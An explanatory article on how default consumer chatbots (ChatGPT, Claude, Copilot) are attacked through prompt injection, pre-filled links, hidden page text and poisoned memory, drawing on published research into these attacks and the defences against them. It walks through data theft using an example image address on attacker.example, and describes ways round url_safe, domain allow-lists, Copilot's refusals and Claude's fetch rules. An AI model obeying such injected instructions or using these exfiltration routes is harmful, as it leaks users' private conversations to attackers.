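# Security vulnerabilities of chatbots in their default configuration

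## What an ordinary chatbot can already read, run and send

A chatbot such as ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini or Copilot is a product that a company builds around a large language model, a program that takes in text and produces text in reply. The vendor adds features such as memory of earlier conversations, web search, a place to run code and a window that displays images. Attackers can also exploit these features. A chatbot's security vulnerabilities in its default configuration are the weaknesses it ships with, when its built-in features are on and the user has not yet linked it to a mailbox, a file store or a company database.

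Researchers group most of the attacks under two names. In prompt injection, someone other than the user puts instructions into text the model reads, for instance by hiding them in a web page, and the model follows them. In a jailbreak, the user words a request so that the model produces something the vendor's safeguards should block. Both depend on how a chatbot assembles the text its model reads.

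### How a chat turn is put together

The model reads much more than the user's question. Before the model answers, the product assembles the context, which is all the text the model will read. The context starts with the system prompt, the vendor's standing instructions. *HackedGPT* (2025), an investigation by the security company Tenable, reports that ChatGPT's system prompt describes the tools the model can call (functions such as web search) and that the user's saved memories are appended to it. The earlier messages from both the user and the chatbot come next, with the contents of any uploaded files, and the new question comes last. If the model calls for a web search, the product runs it and adds the results to the context, and the model continues from there.

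Suppose a user asks a chatbot to summarize an article about mortgages. The context may then hold the vendor's instructions, a memory that the user is going through a divorce, an earlier exchange about her salary, her request, and the article with the comments that strangers left under it. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) describes all of this as "glued together into a sequence of tokens". Tokens are the short pieces of text, often a word or part of one, that a language model processes.

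Some products put a partial barrier between the chatbot and the web pages it reads. When Tenable examined ChatGPT, a second model with no access to the user's memories opened web pages and reported its findings to the main model. This limited what the second model could leak, but the main model still read its findings as part of the conversation.

Vendors wrap each part of the sequence in role tags, which label it as system prompt, user message, tool output, the model's own reasoning or its answer. The system prompt is supposed to outrank user messages, and the model is supposed to use text from a tool to inform its answer but never follow instructions in it. A conventional program can enforce such a rule by storing commands and data separately and refusing to execute the data. A language model can't do this because it processes both in one sequence, computing each new token from everything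 before it, including the tags. Whether it treats a sentence in a web page as a command depends on what it learned in training, so vendors train their models to rank these sources.

Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, measured how much the tags matter inside the model. They built probes, simple classifiers that estimate from a model's internal activations which role the model assigns to each token. To make sure the probes learned only the effect of the tags, they trained them on identical passages of ordinary web text wrapped in each of the five tags. They then applied the probes to a short conversation about gardening in gpt-oss-20b, a model whose weights OpenAI has published. With the correct tags, the model's reasoning scored 85% on average as reasoning. Without any tags, it scored 83%. With the whole conversation wrapped in user tags, it still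 scored 85% as reasoning and only 2% as user text.

The wording of a text affected its scores more than its label did, and an outsider can choose the wording even though only the vendor sets the label. This was also true of text written like a user's message but tagged as tool output, as a command hidden in a web page would be. In one model, such text scored 87.6% as user text and 9.3% as tool output. The scores also correlated with the behaviour of an agent (a model that carries out a task in several steps with tools). Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent send out private data, the attack succeeded in 2% of the cases with the least role confusion and 70% of those with the most.

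Such probes need access to a model's activations. Outsiders have that access for open-weight models but not for the ones behind ChatGPT and Claude, so the evidence on commercial products is less direct. Hidden commands can also fail even when a model lacks this boundary. In a test where a web page told an agent to upload a secret file, Ye and colleagues found that plain injections succeeded in 0 to 2% of attempts on every model except gpt-oss-20b, where they succeeded in 26%. They attribute this resistance to models having memorised familiar attacks, and cite human testers who reach success rates near 100% against models with near-perfect benchmark scores. If they are right, a model's low failure rate on known attacks is a poor guide to how it will handle new ones.

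### The bare model and the default product

The bare model is the language model alone, with no memory, search, code execution or network access. Its context holds only what somebody supplies, and its output is text. Hardly any members of the public use a model this way. OpenAI's *ChatGPT capabilities overview* lists web search, data analysis with code, file and audio uploads, image input and memory among the built-in features. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Free Tier FAQ* lists search, data analysis and uploads for free users too, with usage limits on some of them. Anthropic describes Claude's equivalents in several help articles, chiefly *Use Claude’s chat search and memory to build on previous context* and *Enable and use web search*.

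The table shows how ChatGPT and Claude stood in late 2026, with older findings dated.

| Built-in feature | ChatGPT | Claude |
|---|---|---|
| Memory | On by default outside the EU, as BGR, a technology news site, reported in 2025. "Improved memory" starts off in healthcare and regulated enterprise workspaces. | On by default on the Free, Pro, Max and Ultra plans. On Team and Enterprise plans it starts on in most organisations created from 31 October 2026; in older ones each member must turn it on. |
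| Search of past chats | Memory can draw on past chats, depending on plan and region. | Paid plans only, on by default. |
| Web search | Free and paid plans. The model can start a search at its own discretion. | Available on personal plans. On Team and Enterprise plans an owner must enable it first. |
| Code sandbox (an isolated environment for running code) | Free and paid plans, with a usage limit on the free one. | On by default for Team, with network access to package managers only, and for Enterprise, with network access off in new organisations. Personal plans have a switch in the settings. |
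| Links that pre-fill a prompt | In November 2025 such a link submitted its prompt without a further click. | In early 2026 the link filled the text box and the user pressed Enter. |

A chatbot's "memory" can include several stores of data. OpenAI's *Memory in ChatGPT* includes past chats, saved memories, custom instructions, files in the user's library and content from connected apps such as Gmail, though connecting an app goes beyond the default configuration. Anthropic keeps health, religion, politics and similar subjects out of Claude's memory unless the user opts in. That filter applies only to what Claude saves as memory, while a search of past chats covers all conversations outside projects except those that used linked financial accounts. A search can therefore presumably turn up a chat in which the user discussed an illness.

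A more expensive plan can be more or less exposed by default. Claude's free plan has memory but no search of past chats, so the model can reach more of a paying subscriber's history. But the Enterprise plan starts with tighter network settings than the Team plan, where code in the sandbox can at least contact package managers, the servers from which programmers download software libraries. It is less clear whether code execution is on by default for personal accounts. Anthropic instructs these users to switch it on, while a security report from March 2026 listed it among the features that came with the product.

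*Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes an attack on Claude that used a pre-filled link, the search of past chats and the code sandbox to steal a user's conversation history. Luz, who leads research at the company Oasis Security, writes that the attack required "No integrations, no tools, no MCP servers". MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a standard for connecting chatbots to outside services. Anthropic says that a search of past chats appears in the conversation as a tool call, so Luz's wording makes sense only if "tools" means external tools. He says as much a few paragraphs later, where he attributes the theft to capabilities that ship "out of the box".

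Security reports often use "no tools" to mean that the user added none, which misleads readers who take the phrase literally. The finding in *Claudy Day* concerns the product, where the user didn't need to add anything because the vendor had already supplied what the attacker needed. *Claudy Day* doesn't show that a bare model can look up a user's old conversations or upload a file.

### Who attacks whom

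Willison coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack on databases. In SQL injection, a careless program joins its own command to text that a visitor typed into a form, and the database executes part of that text as a further command. Willison (2024) complained that people were using "prompt injection" to mean jailbreaking. *Prompt Injection versus Jailbreaking Definitions*, on maxime.sh, reproduces his distinction: prompt injection requires untrusted input to be concatenated with a developer's trusted prompt, while jailbreaking attempts to subvert the safety filters built into the model.

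For a consumer chatbot, prompt injection and jailbreaks can be distinguished by who attacks whom. In prompt injection, an outsider attacks the user. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) defines it in similar terms, as a third party's attempt to mislead the system into following malicious instructions or revealing sensitive information. The injection is indirect when the instructions arrive inside content such as a web page or a file. In a jailbreak, the user is the attacker and defeats the vendor's safeguards. If she obtains instructions for making a weapon, this puts third parties at risk but does not expose her own data.

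Ye and colleagues define prompt injection more broadly, to include a user's message that imitates a system prompt, because there too text with little authority takes on a role with more. Grouping the two kinds of attack together is useful for studying the mechanism they share, but less useful for deciding who should worry. Willison observes that developers who equate them tend to dismiss prompt injection as a chatbot embarrassing its vendor, and so overlook a threat to their own customers.

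Pre-filled links show why the attacker's identity is a better guide to what counts as prompt injection than where the text appears. The injected text arrives in the user's own turn, under the user's tag, and the user may even press Enter herself. The model receives it as a user's request, but it is prompt injection because a stranger wrote it and the user never meant to send it.

### Three conditions for data theft

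An injected instruction can give an attacker someone's data only if the system combines three capabilities, which Willison calls the "lethal trifecta". The system must have access to private data, take in untrusted content (text or images that an attacker controls), and be able to send data to the attacker. Any route for sending that data is called an exfiltration channel. Willison wrote for people who combine tools themselves, but the same conditions apply to a chatbot that comes with its tools installed.

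A bare model can reply to the user but cannot open a connection to anyone else. It sees private information only if the user types it into the conversation, and a stranger's writing, such as an email, only if she pastes it in. Hidden instructions in that email might slant the model's summary or add a link to it, but her data stays in the chat unless she acts on the answer.

A default session meets all three conditions. Memory and past chats supply the private data, while search results, web pages, uploaded files and pre-filled links let in text from strangers. In July 2026, Willison identified the tool that lets "regular Claude chat" fetch web pages as a way to send data out. Each request sends the page's address to the server that hosts it, so any private facts written into the address would be sent too. The same tool can bring in hostile instructions, so together with memory it is enough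 to meet all three conditions.

OpenAI's help article *Lockdown Mode* describes an optional setting for people who handle sensitive data, and the features it restricts show how data could leave ChatGPT. With the setting on, ChatGPT browses only stored copies of pages and may not show images in ordinary answers. It cannot download files for data analysis, and users cannot give network access to code written in Canvas, its editing workspace. The setting also disables deep research and agent mode, which work through many web sources or steps on the user's behalf. Memory and file uploads are unchanged. OpenAI has therefore left the first two conditions largely in place and restricted the third, and it warns that a malicious instruction in an uploaded file can still produce a wrong answer. OpenAI considers the setting unnecessary for most users, who keep the ordinary connections and whatever protections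 the standard product has.

Those protections can block a particular theft even when a session has all three capabilities. Claude's fetch tool, for instance, may visit only exact addresses that the user entered or that a web search returned. As Willison explains, it therefore blocks an instruction to attach the user's recent answers to an attacker's address and open the result. An attacker has to find a route that the rules don't cover, and researchers have repeatedly found such routes. Willison's list of affected products includes ChatGPT in April 2023, Google's Bard (since renamed Gemini) in November 2023, Microsoft Copilot in August 2024 and Claude's iOS app in December 2024. He writes that the vendors fixed almost all of these flaws promptly, usually by locking down the route through which the data left.

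## How an attacker's text enters a chat and stays there

A prompt injection works only if the victim, or the product acting for her, brings the attacker's text into the context, because an outsider can't type into someone else's chat. She may paste the text, follow a link or upload a file that contains it, or ask a question that leads the chatbot to a web page where it appears. These routes differ in how much she has to do and in whether she could notice the text in time.

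### Copied text

*New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, by the software engineer Roman Samoilenko, describes an attack through the clipboard that Willison (2023) called "ingenious". Samoilenko built a web page with a script that added a prompt to any text a visitor copied. The visitor can't see the added prompt until she pastes the text into ChatGPT's text box, where she can still delete it. If she presses Enter without deleting it, the model treats it as part of her own message.

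Samoilenko's added prompt instructed ChatGPT to end its answer with an invisible image whose address contained data from the chat. A longer version included the instruction to add the same image to every later answer, so a single paste affected the rest of the conversation.

Samoilenko reported that the attack did not always work. ChatGPT's output is partly random, so a prompt that worked once could fail the next time. Success also depended on the topic of the earlier conversation, the position of the prompt in the pasted text, and how the user phrased her next message. ChatGPT would readily attach her previous prompts or her code to the image address, but Samoilenko found it very difficult to make it attach passwords. When ChatGPT was responding slowly, the user might also see the strange text appear word by word. His tests show that the attack was possible, but he used only the ChatGPT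 version of 14 March 2023 and gave no success rate.

### Links that carry a prompt

For convenience, several chatbots accept a prompt inside a web address, usually after the characters "q=". Microsoft (2026) lists such addresses for Copilot, ChatGPT, Claude, Perplexity and Grok. An attacker can write the prompt and send the link to a victim. If the link only fills the text box, the victim can see the prompt and must press Enter to send it. If the link also submits the prompt, the model is already answering by the time she can read it.

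Clicking a ChatGPT link used to submit the prompt in its address without confirmation, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025). Other parts of the address let the attacker choose the model and turn on web search. The prompt could be a short request to summarize a page that contained the harmful instructions, so a victim who read the submitted message would find nothing alarming in it.

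Tenable reported the self-submitting links on 15 April 2025, and OpenAI said on 30 April that a fix had reached all users. On 6 May Tenable found that the links still worked. On 11 July OpenAI said it had added protection based on a header, a line of information that browsers attach to a request, showing whether the request came from the same site or a different one. Tenable's *HackedGPT* report of November 2025 still described self-submitting links in the present tense but did not mention the July change, so it is weak evidence that the links still submitted themselves in November.

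A link to the genuine website of Microsoft's Copilot could also contain a prompt. Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot Personal, the consumer version, that began when the user clicked such a link. The prompt ran as soon as the page loaded. It instructed Copilot to put personal details into a web address on the researchers' server and open that address.

As safeguards, Copilot usually refused to open a web address without a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from the address before opening it. The researchers got around the refusal by presenting the task as a puzzle that the user needed help with. They then found that Copilot removed the data only from the first request. When the prompt told Copilot to do every action twice, it deleted a secret test phrase from the address on the first attempt but sent it on the second.

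After that, each page the server returned contained the next question, so the attacker could choose what to ask for based on earlier answers. Anyone who inspected the original link would see only the opening request. Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026) lists the user's name, her location and details from her chat history among the stolen data. The theft continued after she closed the chat. According to The Next Web, Varonis reported the flaw in August 2025 and Microsoft patched it in January 2026. Varonis says Microsoft 365 Copilot, the business version, was not affected.

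Seven months later, Varonis published *CoSnitch* (2026), a second one-click attack on Copilot Personal. In this attack, "q=" alone only fills the prompt box, and an undocumented second parameter makes the prompt run. The researchers learned of this parameter by repeatedly asking Copilot why a prompt could never run by itself. In one answer, Copilot gave the parameter's name but wrongly stated that it no longer worked. Microsoft shipped patches on 18 August 2026, eight months after Varonis reported the problem. *Reprompt* had described "q=" as sufficient to run a prompt. Microsoft may have changed this when it patched the earlier attack, but Varonis does not explain the difference.

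Companies have already used such links on the public. Over 60 days, Microsoft's researchers looked at links to chatbots in email traffic and found about 50 different prompts in which 31 companies asked the chatbot to remember them favourably. The prompts were typically behind a button labelled "Summarize with AI", and combined a request for a summary with a request to remember the company as a trusted source. All 31 were real businesses, including a security vendor. Free software for making the buttons was available online.

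Microsoft counted attempts but did not measure how many changed a chatbot's memory. It says that results varied between products and over time, and that in several cases it could no longer reproduce behaviour others had reported. Anyone could see the prompt by holding the pointer over the summary button and reading the full address, but few people do that before clicking. Where the link fills in the text box without sending the prompt, reading the box is a better check, though in Luz's attack on Claude the box did not show the part of the prompt hidden in HTML.

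### Text that the user cannot see

A chatbot may receive all the text in a web page's code, including text styled so that a person cannot see it. In one of the *CoSnitch* tests, a page contained an ordinary article on cloud security and a paragraph in white type one pixel high. When the user asked Copilot for a summary, it gave a plausible one but also followed the instructions in the white paragraph. Varonis says that comments in the page's code and its metadata fields would have worked just as well, because the model processes the text and not its appearance. Willison relays a similar case from the security company PromptArmor, in which one-pixel type on a web page misled Antigravity, Google's coding tool.

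An attacker can hide instructions inside an ordinary sentence by encoding them in invisible characters. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, includes characters that most programs don't display. The user sees only the sentence, but the hidden characters may still reach the model unless the product removes them first. They can also stay hidden when copied and pasted, whereas white or tiny text usually becomes visible before the user sends it, because a plain text box drops the colour and size.

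Files and images can also carry an attacker's instructions into a chat. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, has tested both on ChatGPT. In his post *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, a user asks about a PDF that contains an attacker's instructions. ChatGPT had placed recent conversations in the system prompt, so the attacker could direct the model to those as well as to the document. In an earlier test, Rehberger uploaded an image with instructions in it, and ChatGPT followed them when he asked for an analysis. The victim has to open the stranger's file in the chatbot, but she has little reason to be suspicious, because people use chatbots to summarize unfamiliar documents.

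### Web pages and Tenable's seven findings

With web search, the victim doesn't have to handle the attacker's text. Tenable's *HackedGPT* report describes seven vulnerabilities and techniques in ChatGPT, and two of them start with a web page. In one, the attacker leaves instructions in the comment section of a blog, and ChatGPT reads them when a user asks for a summary of the post. The attacker doesn't need to control the site, so a popular news site with open comments would work.

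The other attack works when the user only asks a question. Tenable made several websites on obscure subjects, including one about its own research team, called LLM Ninjas, and waited for search engines to list them. When a researcher asked ChatGPT about the team, it found the site and followed the instructions Tenable had put there. This is a zero-click attack because the victim doesn't click a link or name a page. Tenable's *OpenAI SearchGPT Results Tampering with Prompt Injection* (2025) explains how the site got into the search results. The site recognized OpenAI's crawler, the program that collects pages for search, by the headers it sent. It showed the page with the instructions only to the crawler and gave Bing and human visitors a harmless one.

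An attacker still has to get the page into the results for a question that the victim will ask. Tenable made this easy by choosing a subject that no other site covered. For a common question, the page would have to compete with established sites, although the advisory notes that attackers can raise its rank with ordinary search optimization.

Neither route reached private data on its own, because the separate browsing model could not read the user's memories. The remaining findings show how an attacker could get past this barrier. Tenable's instructions made the browsing model end its summary with further instructions. When the user sent the next message, the main model reread the conversation, found those instructions in what appeared to be its own earlier answer, and followed them. Tenable calls this conversation injection.

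The user would normally have seen these instructions in the summary, but a display bug on the ChatGPT website hid anything after the first word on the opening line of a code block. The model still read text placed there.

To send data out, the attacker also had to pass "url_safe", OpenAI's check on the links and images in an answer. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) found that the check approved every address on bing.com. Bing gives each site in its results a bing.com address that redirects to the site, so links to the attacker's pages in those results also passed the check. Attackers can't add data to these addresses, so Tenable listed one page on Bing for each letter of the alphabet and had ChatGPT spell out the stolen text by loading the matching pages in order.

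Most of the research used ChatGPT 4o, and Tenable repeated several of the attacks on ChatGPT 5. The table lists the versions named in Tenable's demonstrations and the information about fixes in its reports. One of these reports, *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT*, covers the comment and memory attacks.

| Finding | What the attacker gains | Version in the demonstration | Fix |
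|---|---|---|---|
| Instructions in a blog comment | Control of the summary | 4o and 5 | None by March 2025 |
| Instructions on a page found by search | Control of the answer to a plain question | 4o and 5 | None by March 2025 |
| Self-submitting link | A prompt in the user's own turn | Not stated | OpenAI reported protection in July 2025 |
| Bing redirect addresses | Links and images that pass the safety check | 4o and 5 | None by March 2025; OpenAI reported an improved check in July |
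| Conversation injection | Control of the main model | 5 | None by March 2025 |
| Text hidden in a code block | Concealment from the user | 5 | Not stated |
| Memory injection | Control of later chats | 4o | None by March 2025 |

Tenable wrote in November 2025 that it had worked with OpenAI to fix "some of the vulnerabilities", and The Hacker News, a security news site, also reported that OpenAI had addressed some of them, but neither specified which. Tenable published a fix date only for the self-submitting link. ChatGPT 5 came out after the March advisories, so the attacks Tenable demonstrated on it evidently still worked some months later.

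Web pages could still shape ChatGPT's answers in 2026. In May, The Hacker News (2026) reported on ChatGPhish, an attack found by researchers at the company Permiso. The attacker adds a short instruction to a web page, telling ChatGPT to write any summary of the page in a fixed format. In an example from Permiso, the format includes a warning that a new device has joined the user's account. ChatGPT displays the warning with a working link or a QR code, so it looks like a message from OpenAI. If the user scans the code, her phone opens an address she has never seen written out. This attack needs no access to her data, but it fails if she ignores the warning.

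### How an injected instruction persists

An attacker's instruction stays in a chat without any special technique, because the context for each new question includes the earlier messages. Samoilenko's repeated image and Tenable's conversation injection both relied on this, and both ended when the user started a new chat.

Long-term memory can carry an attacker's text into later chats. ChatGPT's model saves a memory by calling a tool, and the product then adds the saved text to the system prompt of later chats. If an injected instruction gets the model to save the attacker's text, that text appears in each new chat next to OpenAI's own instructions. The page or file it came from is no longer in the context, and the user may have forgotten it.

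In May 2024, soon after OpenAI introduced ChatGPT's memory feature, Rehberger showed that an attacker's instructions could add false memories. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT: Hacking Memories with Prompt Injection* describes three attempts. The instructions worked when placed in an uploaded image or a linked Google document. When they were on a web page, ChatGPT fetched the text but did not save anything.

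Rehberger's tests showed that ChatGPT could still use the memory tool when outside text was in the chat, though he had first suspected that OpenAI blocked it. When the page asked for a picture as well as a memory, ChatGPT sometimes produced both. Delaying the memory request until a later turn also worked a few times, though unreliably. The protection was the model's tendency to refuse, so different wording could defeat it. A successful injection could add dozens of memories at once or delete all existing ones. The user's only warning was a small "Memory updated" notice above the answer, which she could click to see the change.

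Rehberger soon found a more serious use for false memories than distorting advice. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes a website that planted a standing instruction in ChatGPT's Mac app. From then on, the app sent every message and answer to the attacker through an invisible image, in new chats as well as the current one. OpenAI blocked this use of images in September 2024. That stopped the theft, but websites and documents could still write memories, so an attacker's instructions could still carry over into new chats.

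Tenable's memory injection worked in the same way a few months later, starting from a blog comment. Gemini and Copilot have had the same weakness. OODA Loop's *New hack uses prompt injection to corrupt Gemini’s long-term memory* describes how Rehberger got around a Google defence that restricts Gemini's use of sensitive tools while it processes untrusted text. The hidden paragraph in the *CoSnitch* test also wrote to Copilot's memory. Varonis used such a memory to make Copilot describe a known software flaw as harmless. The memory belonged to the account, so it stayed after a password change or logout until the user deleted it.

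The controls OpenAI now describes mostly help users find and remove a bad memory after ChatGPT has saved it. Users can read a summary of what ChatGPT remembers, correct or delete entries, and turn memory off. An answer may also come with a list of the memories or past chats that influenced it. OpenAI warns that neither the summary nor the list is complete. Deleting the chat where an attack took place may leave the planted memory behind, because ChatGPT stores saved memories separately.

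ChatGPT's memory also depends less on explicit saves than it once did. Windows Report's *OpenAI Upgrades ChatGPT Memory With Smarter Recall and Better Personalization* describes a background process called "dreaming", which selects useful information from past chats. Rehberger and Tenable attacked the tool that saves individual memories. An attacker's text might also enter memory through the background process, without a call to that tool, but their demonstrations did not test this.

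Temporary chats are the only control that prevents an attacker's text from being saved to memory, because they never create or update memories. A user who wants a summary of an unfamiliar document can ask for it there, and nothing in the document will carry over into her other conversations unless she saves the chat. The document can still affect the answers in that chat, and it may also be able to reach her existing memories unless she selected the "Unpersonalized" option before she began.

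## How private data leaves a chat

Once an attacker's instructions are in the context, the model can follow them and collect private facts from the same context. The facts must still leave the chat and reach a computer the attacker controls, usually inside the address of a page or an image.

### Images that carry data

Chatbots format their answers in Markdown, a notation in which an image is written as a web address with a few marks around it. The chat window shows the picture in place of the address. Suppose a user has told a chatbot that she is "quitting in May", and later asks it to summarize a web page that contains hidden instructions. An attacker can then steal what she said in four steps.

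1. The instructions tell the model to end its summary with an image and to put the user's plans in the image's address. The model writes `https://attacker.example/dot.png?d=quitting%20in%20May`, in which "%20" stands for a space.
2. The chat window treats this text as an image, so the user's browser requests it from attacker.example.
3. The server records the full address in its log, as web servers commonly do, and returns a transparent image one pixel wide.
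4. The attacker reads the log and finds "quitting in May".

The model writes an image address that contains the private data, and the user's browser automatically requests the image from the attacker's server, as it would any picture. An ordinary link can carry the same data, but the user has to click it. If the model opens the address with its own browsing tool, the request comes from the vendor's computers, and the attacker's server still logs the data.

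A chatbot can leak data while returning an ordinary summary, so the user and any safety check that examines only the answer can miss the leak. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested this with an AI agent that ran on the researchers' own machines and automatically previewed links. The agent leaked data with a probability of about 89% while giving harmless-looking answers, and checks on those answers missed 95% of the successful attacks. These figures come from an experimental agent and are not leak rates for any commercial chatbot.

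A vendor can stop data from leaking through images by refusing to load images from outside sites. Rehberger reported the problem in early 2023 to OpenAI and to Microsoft, whose Bing Chat, the predecessor of Copilot, was also affected. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft fixed it that May with a Content-Security-Policy, a header that limits which sites a page can load material from. OpenAI had no bug bounty programme at the time, and Rehberger's emails to the company had little effect.

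### OpenAI's first checks

ChatGPT still leaked data through images in December 2023, when Rehberger demonstrated the theft live on a volunteer. The next day he noticed a new safeguard, which he describes in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. The ChatGPT website now sent each image's address to a service called url_safe on OpenAI's servers before displaying the image. If the service returned "false", the browser did not request the image.

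OpenAI did not publish the rules behind the check, so researchers had to work them out by testing addresses. Rehberger prepared 36 images on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them passed. He could find no reason why the image for "a" loaded and the one for "d" did not. He used the characters that passed to send out the word "hi" in two requests. The iPhone app had no check, because OpenAI had built it into the website and would have to add it to each app separately. The Mac app also lacked it, so the memory Rehberger planted could later send out every message through an invisible image.

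The security company Imperva studied the check shortly after ChatGPT gained its memory feature. Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* concludes that an address passed if it already appeared in text the user had supplied. This should have stopped the theft of "quitting in May", because the model would have made up the address during the attack. But the check also searched the user's custom instructions, the standing preferences that ChatGPT applies to every chat. An attacker who altered those, for instance through a flaw in the website, could store addresses there in advance. The check also accepted any domain without a path after it, even if the user had not mentioned it.

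Imperva found three ways to send out a secret one character at a time under these rules.

| Method | What the attacker prepares | How ChatGPT sends the letter "c" | Drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| One address per character | A list of addresses in the custom instructions | It loads the address that ends in "/c" | The list uses up much of the 3,000 characters allowed |
| One long address | A single address that ends in the digits and the alphabet | It loads the address cut off after "c" | ChatGPT displays the images more slowly |
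| One domain per character | A set of registered domains | It loads an image from the domain for "c" | Each domain costs $1 to $2 |

The second method worked because the check searched the user's text for the address and accepted a match inside a longer address. All three methods were slow, and Imperva judged that stealing large amounts of data unnoticed had become much harder. Splitting a secret over several requests also makes the theft less reliable. In the *Silent Egress* tests, it reduced the main measure of leakage by 73%.

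Rehberger had pointed out two reasons for this in 2023. Requests for several images can arrive out of order, and a browser may reuse its stored copy of an image instead of requesting it again. If ChatGPT spelled out "quitting" with one image per letter, the browser might request "t" and "i" only once each, so the attacker would receive "quitng" even if the requests arrived in order. The attacker could probably guess that word, but a password with missing letters would be much less useful.

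### Approved domains that accept a stranger's data

The check also approved some domains regardless of what the user had typed. Tenable's Bing method used one of these domains to spell out data through redirects to the attacker's pages. Tenable sent OpenAI the full report in December 2024 and had asked for updates six times by early March, when the flaw had still not been fixed.

Rehberger found a more useful domain, windows.net. Microsoft's cloud customers can create storage accounts with addresses under that domain and read a log of every request to them. An attacker could have ChatGPT add any text to a storage account's address, which Bing's fixed redirects did not allow. In the test described on Embrace The Red, one image request sent the "recent conversation" part of the system prompt to Rehberger's storage account.

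He had reported this bypass in October 2024, along with a similar one involving apache.org. The windows.net bypass still worked when he returned to it the following year. He recommended that OpenAI publish the list of approved domains and let business customers change it. Around August 2025, OpenAI strengthened the check, which stopped the attacks he had shown in public.

Other companies' allow-lists have failed in the same way. The email program Superhuman let its AI assistant show images from docs.google.com in its answers. Google Forms runs on that domain, and a form can store data sent in a web address. Willison relays an account of an attack in which one hostile email made the assistant send the contents of dozens of other emails to an attacker's form. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and fixed the flaw.

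Salesforce, which sells customer-management software, had approved a domain and then let its registration expire. Researchers at Noma Security registered the domain and received customer data from Salesforce's AI agent. Salesforce corrected its list of approved domains and added a second control on the links its agent could produce. The list that came with Google's coding tool Antigravity included webhook.site, a service that anyone can use to record incoming requests.

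The Superhuman and Salesforce cases go beyond a chatbot's default configuration because the assistant is connected to a person's or company's records, but the weakness is the same as with windows.net. An attacker only needs an address where he can read what arrives, on any domain in the vendor's list of trusted domains. To rule this out, the vendor would have to know every service on every approved domain and keep checking, because companies add services and domains change hands. The attack on Claude in the next section uses Anthropic's own approved address for file uploads.

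### Approving exact addresses

In January 2026 OpenAI explained a stricter design in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, and a blog post, *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*. The post gives two reasons why a list of trusted sites is not enough. A trusted site may redirect the request elsewhere, as Bing did. A strict list would also produce so many warnings that users would learn to click through them.

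OpenAI therefore checks the exact address of a page or image before ChatGPT loads it automatically. The check uses an index of public web addresses, recorded by a crawler that has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the full address is in the index, ChatGPT loads it. Otherwise, the product directs the model to try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from their conversation.

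No crawler would have recorded `https://attacker.example/dot.png?d=quitting%20in%20May`, because nobody had written that address before the attack. An address that existed independently of the chat can't contain the user's secret, except by coincidence. This guarantee is stronger than a domain list's, because it doesn't depend on who owns the site or what it does with incoming data.

OpenAI claims only to protect against leaks through the web address itself when the product fetches something. It does not promise that a page is truthful or free of hostile instructions. The user can also override the protection by opening a link after the warning.

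Even when a model can load only public addresses, its choice of address can reveal private data. An attacker can publish one page per letter, wait for OpenAI's crawler to index them, and tell the model to load the pages that spell the secret. Rehberger described the trick in 2023. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI acknowledges in its paper that the trick still works in principle. Rehberger notes that a fair-sized blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough for the letters and digits. With thousands of pages, an attacker could assign one to each common word.

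Rehberger suggests that ChatGPT could refuse to visit the same address twice in a session, or reuse a stored copy for a few minutes, so that repeated letters would never reach the attacker. He had not tested whether OpenAI does either. He also warns that the check protects only features whose developers remember to use it, as the iPhone and Mac apps had shown. OpenAI says the check now covers page visits and bookmarks in its Atlas browser, and searches and page visits in deep research.

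Instructing the model to keep secrets is a less dependable defence than checking addresses, because it depends on how the rule is worded. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested agents that held a confidential value while they read hostile content. A rule against revealing the value "in any form" reduced the leak rate from 31.9% to zero. When the rule listed particular forbidden behaviours without that phrase, the leak rate was 48.8%.

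The same researchers tried their attacks on the ChatGPT product and saw no leaks in 48 valid trials, although a model they accessed through OpenAI's programming interface leaked data in up to 100% of trials. They could not see inside the product, so they don't say what stopped the attacks, but the address check may have contributed. Zero leaks in 48 trials is also consistent with a true leak rate of up to about 6%, and an attack designed specifically for ChatGPT might succeed more often.

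OpenAI told users that even in Lockdown Mode, data might escape through connected apps, unforeseen combinations of features or new techniques, according to a statement quoted in The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*.

### Spelling out a secret with Claude's fetch tool

Anthropic instead relies on a rule that Claude's fetch tool may open only addresses it has been given. *Web fetch tool*, Anthropic's developer documentation, lists the permitted sources of these addresses as the user's messages, the results of certain tools, search results, and pages Claude has already fetched. The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. Ordinary code enforces these rules, so a prompt can't bypass them by persuading the model.

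Willison tested the consumer version of Claude when the tool came out in September 2025 and found that it could not open an address it had made up itself. But the rule works only if the attacker's addresses stay out of the permitted sources, and Willison (2025) pointed out that user messages are not always safe, because many developers paste outside text into them. A pre-filled link does something similar in ordinary Claude. It puts the attacker's words into the user's message, and any addresses in those words would presumably count as the user's own.

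In July 2026 Ayush Paul showed that fetched pages were a weak point too. He built a website that claimed to be protected against abuse and asked AI assistants to identify themselves by finding their user's profile in an alphabetical directory. Claude opened the link for the first letter of the user's name, then chose the second letter from the links on the next page, and so on. Claude never wrote an address itself, so it obeyed the rule at every step. The site showed these instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made the trap harder for anyone else to find.

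Willison (2026) reports that Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer this way. The method also avoided the problems with order and repeated letters that come with using images. Claude had to open each page before it could see the next links, so the requests arrived in order, and a repeated letter led to a new page deeper in the directory.

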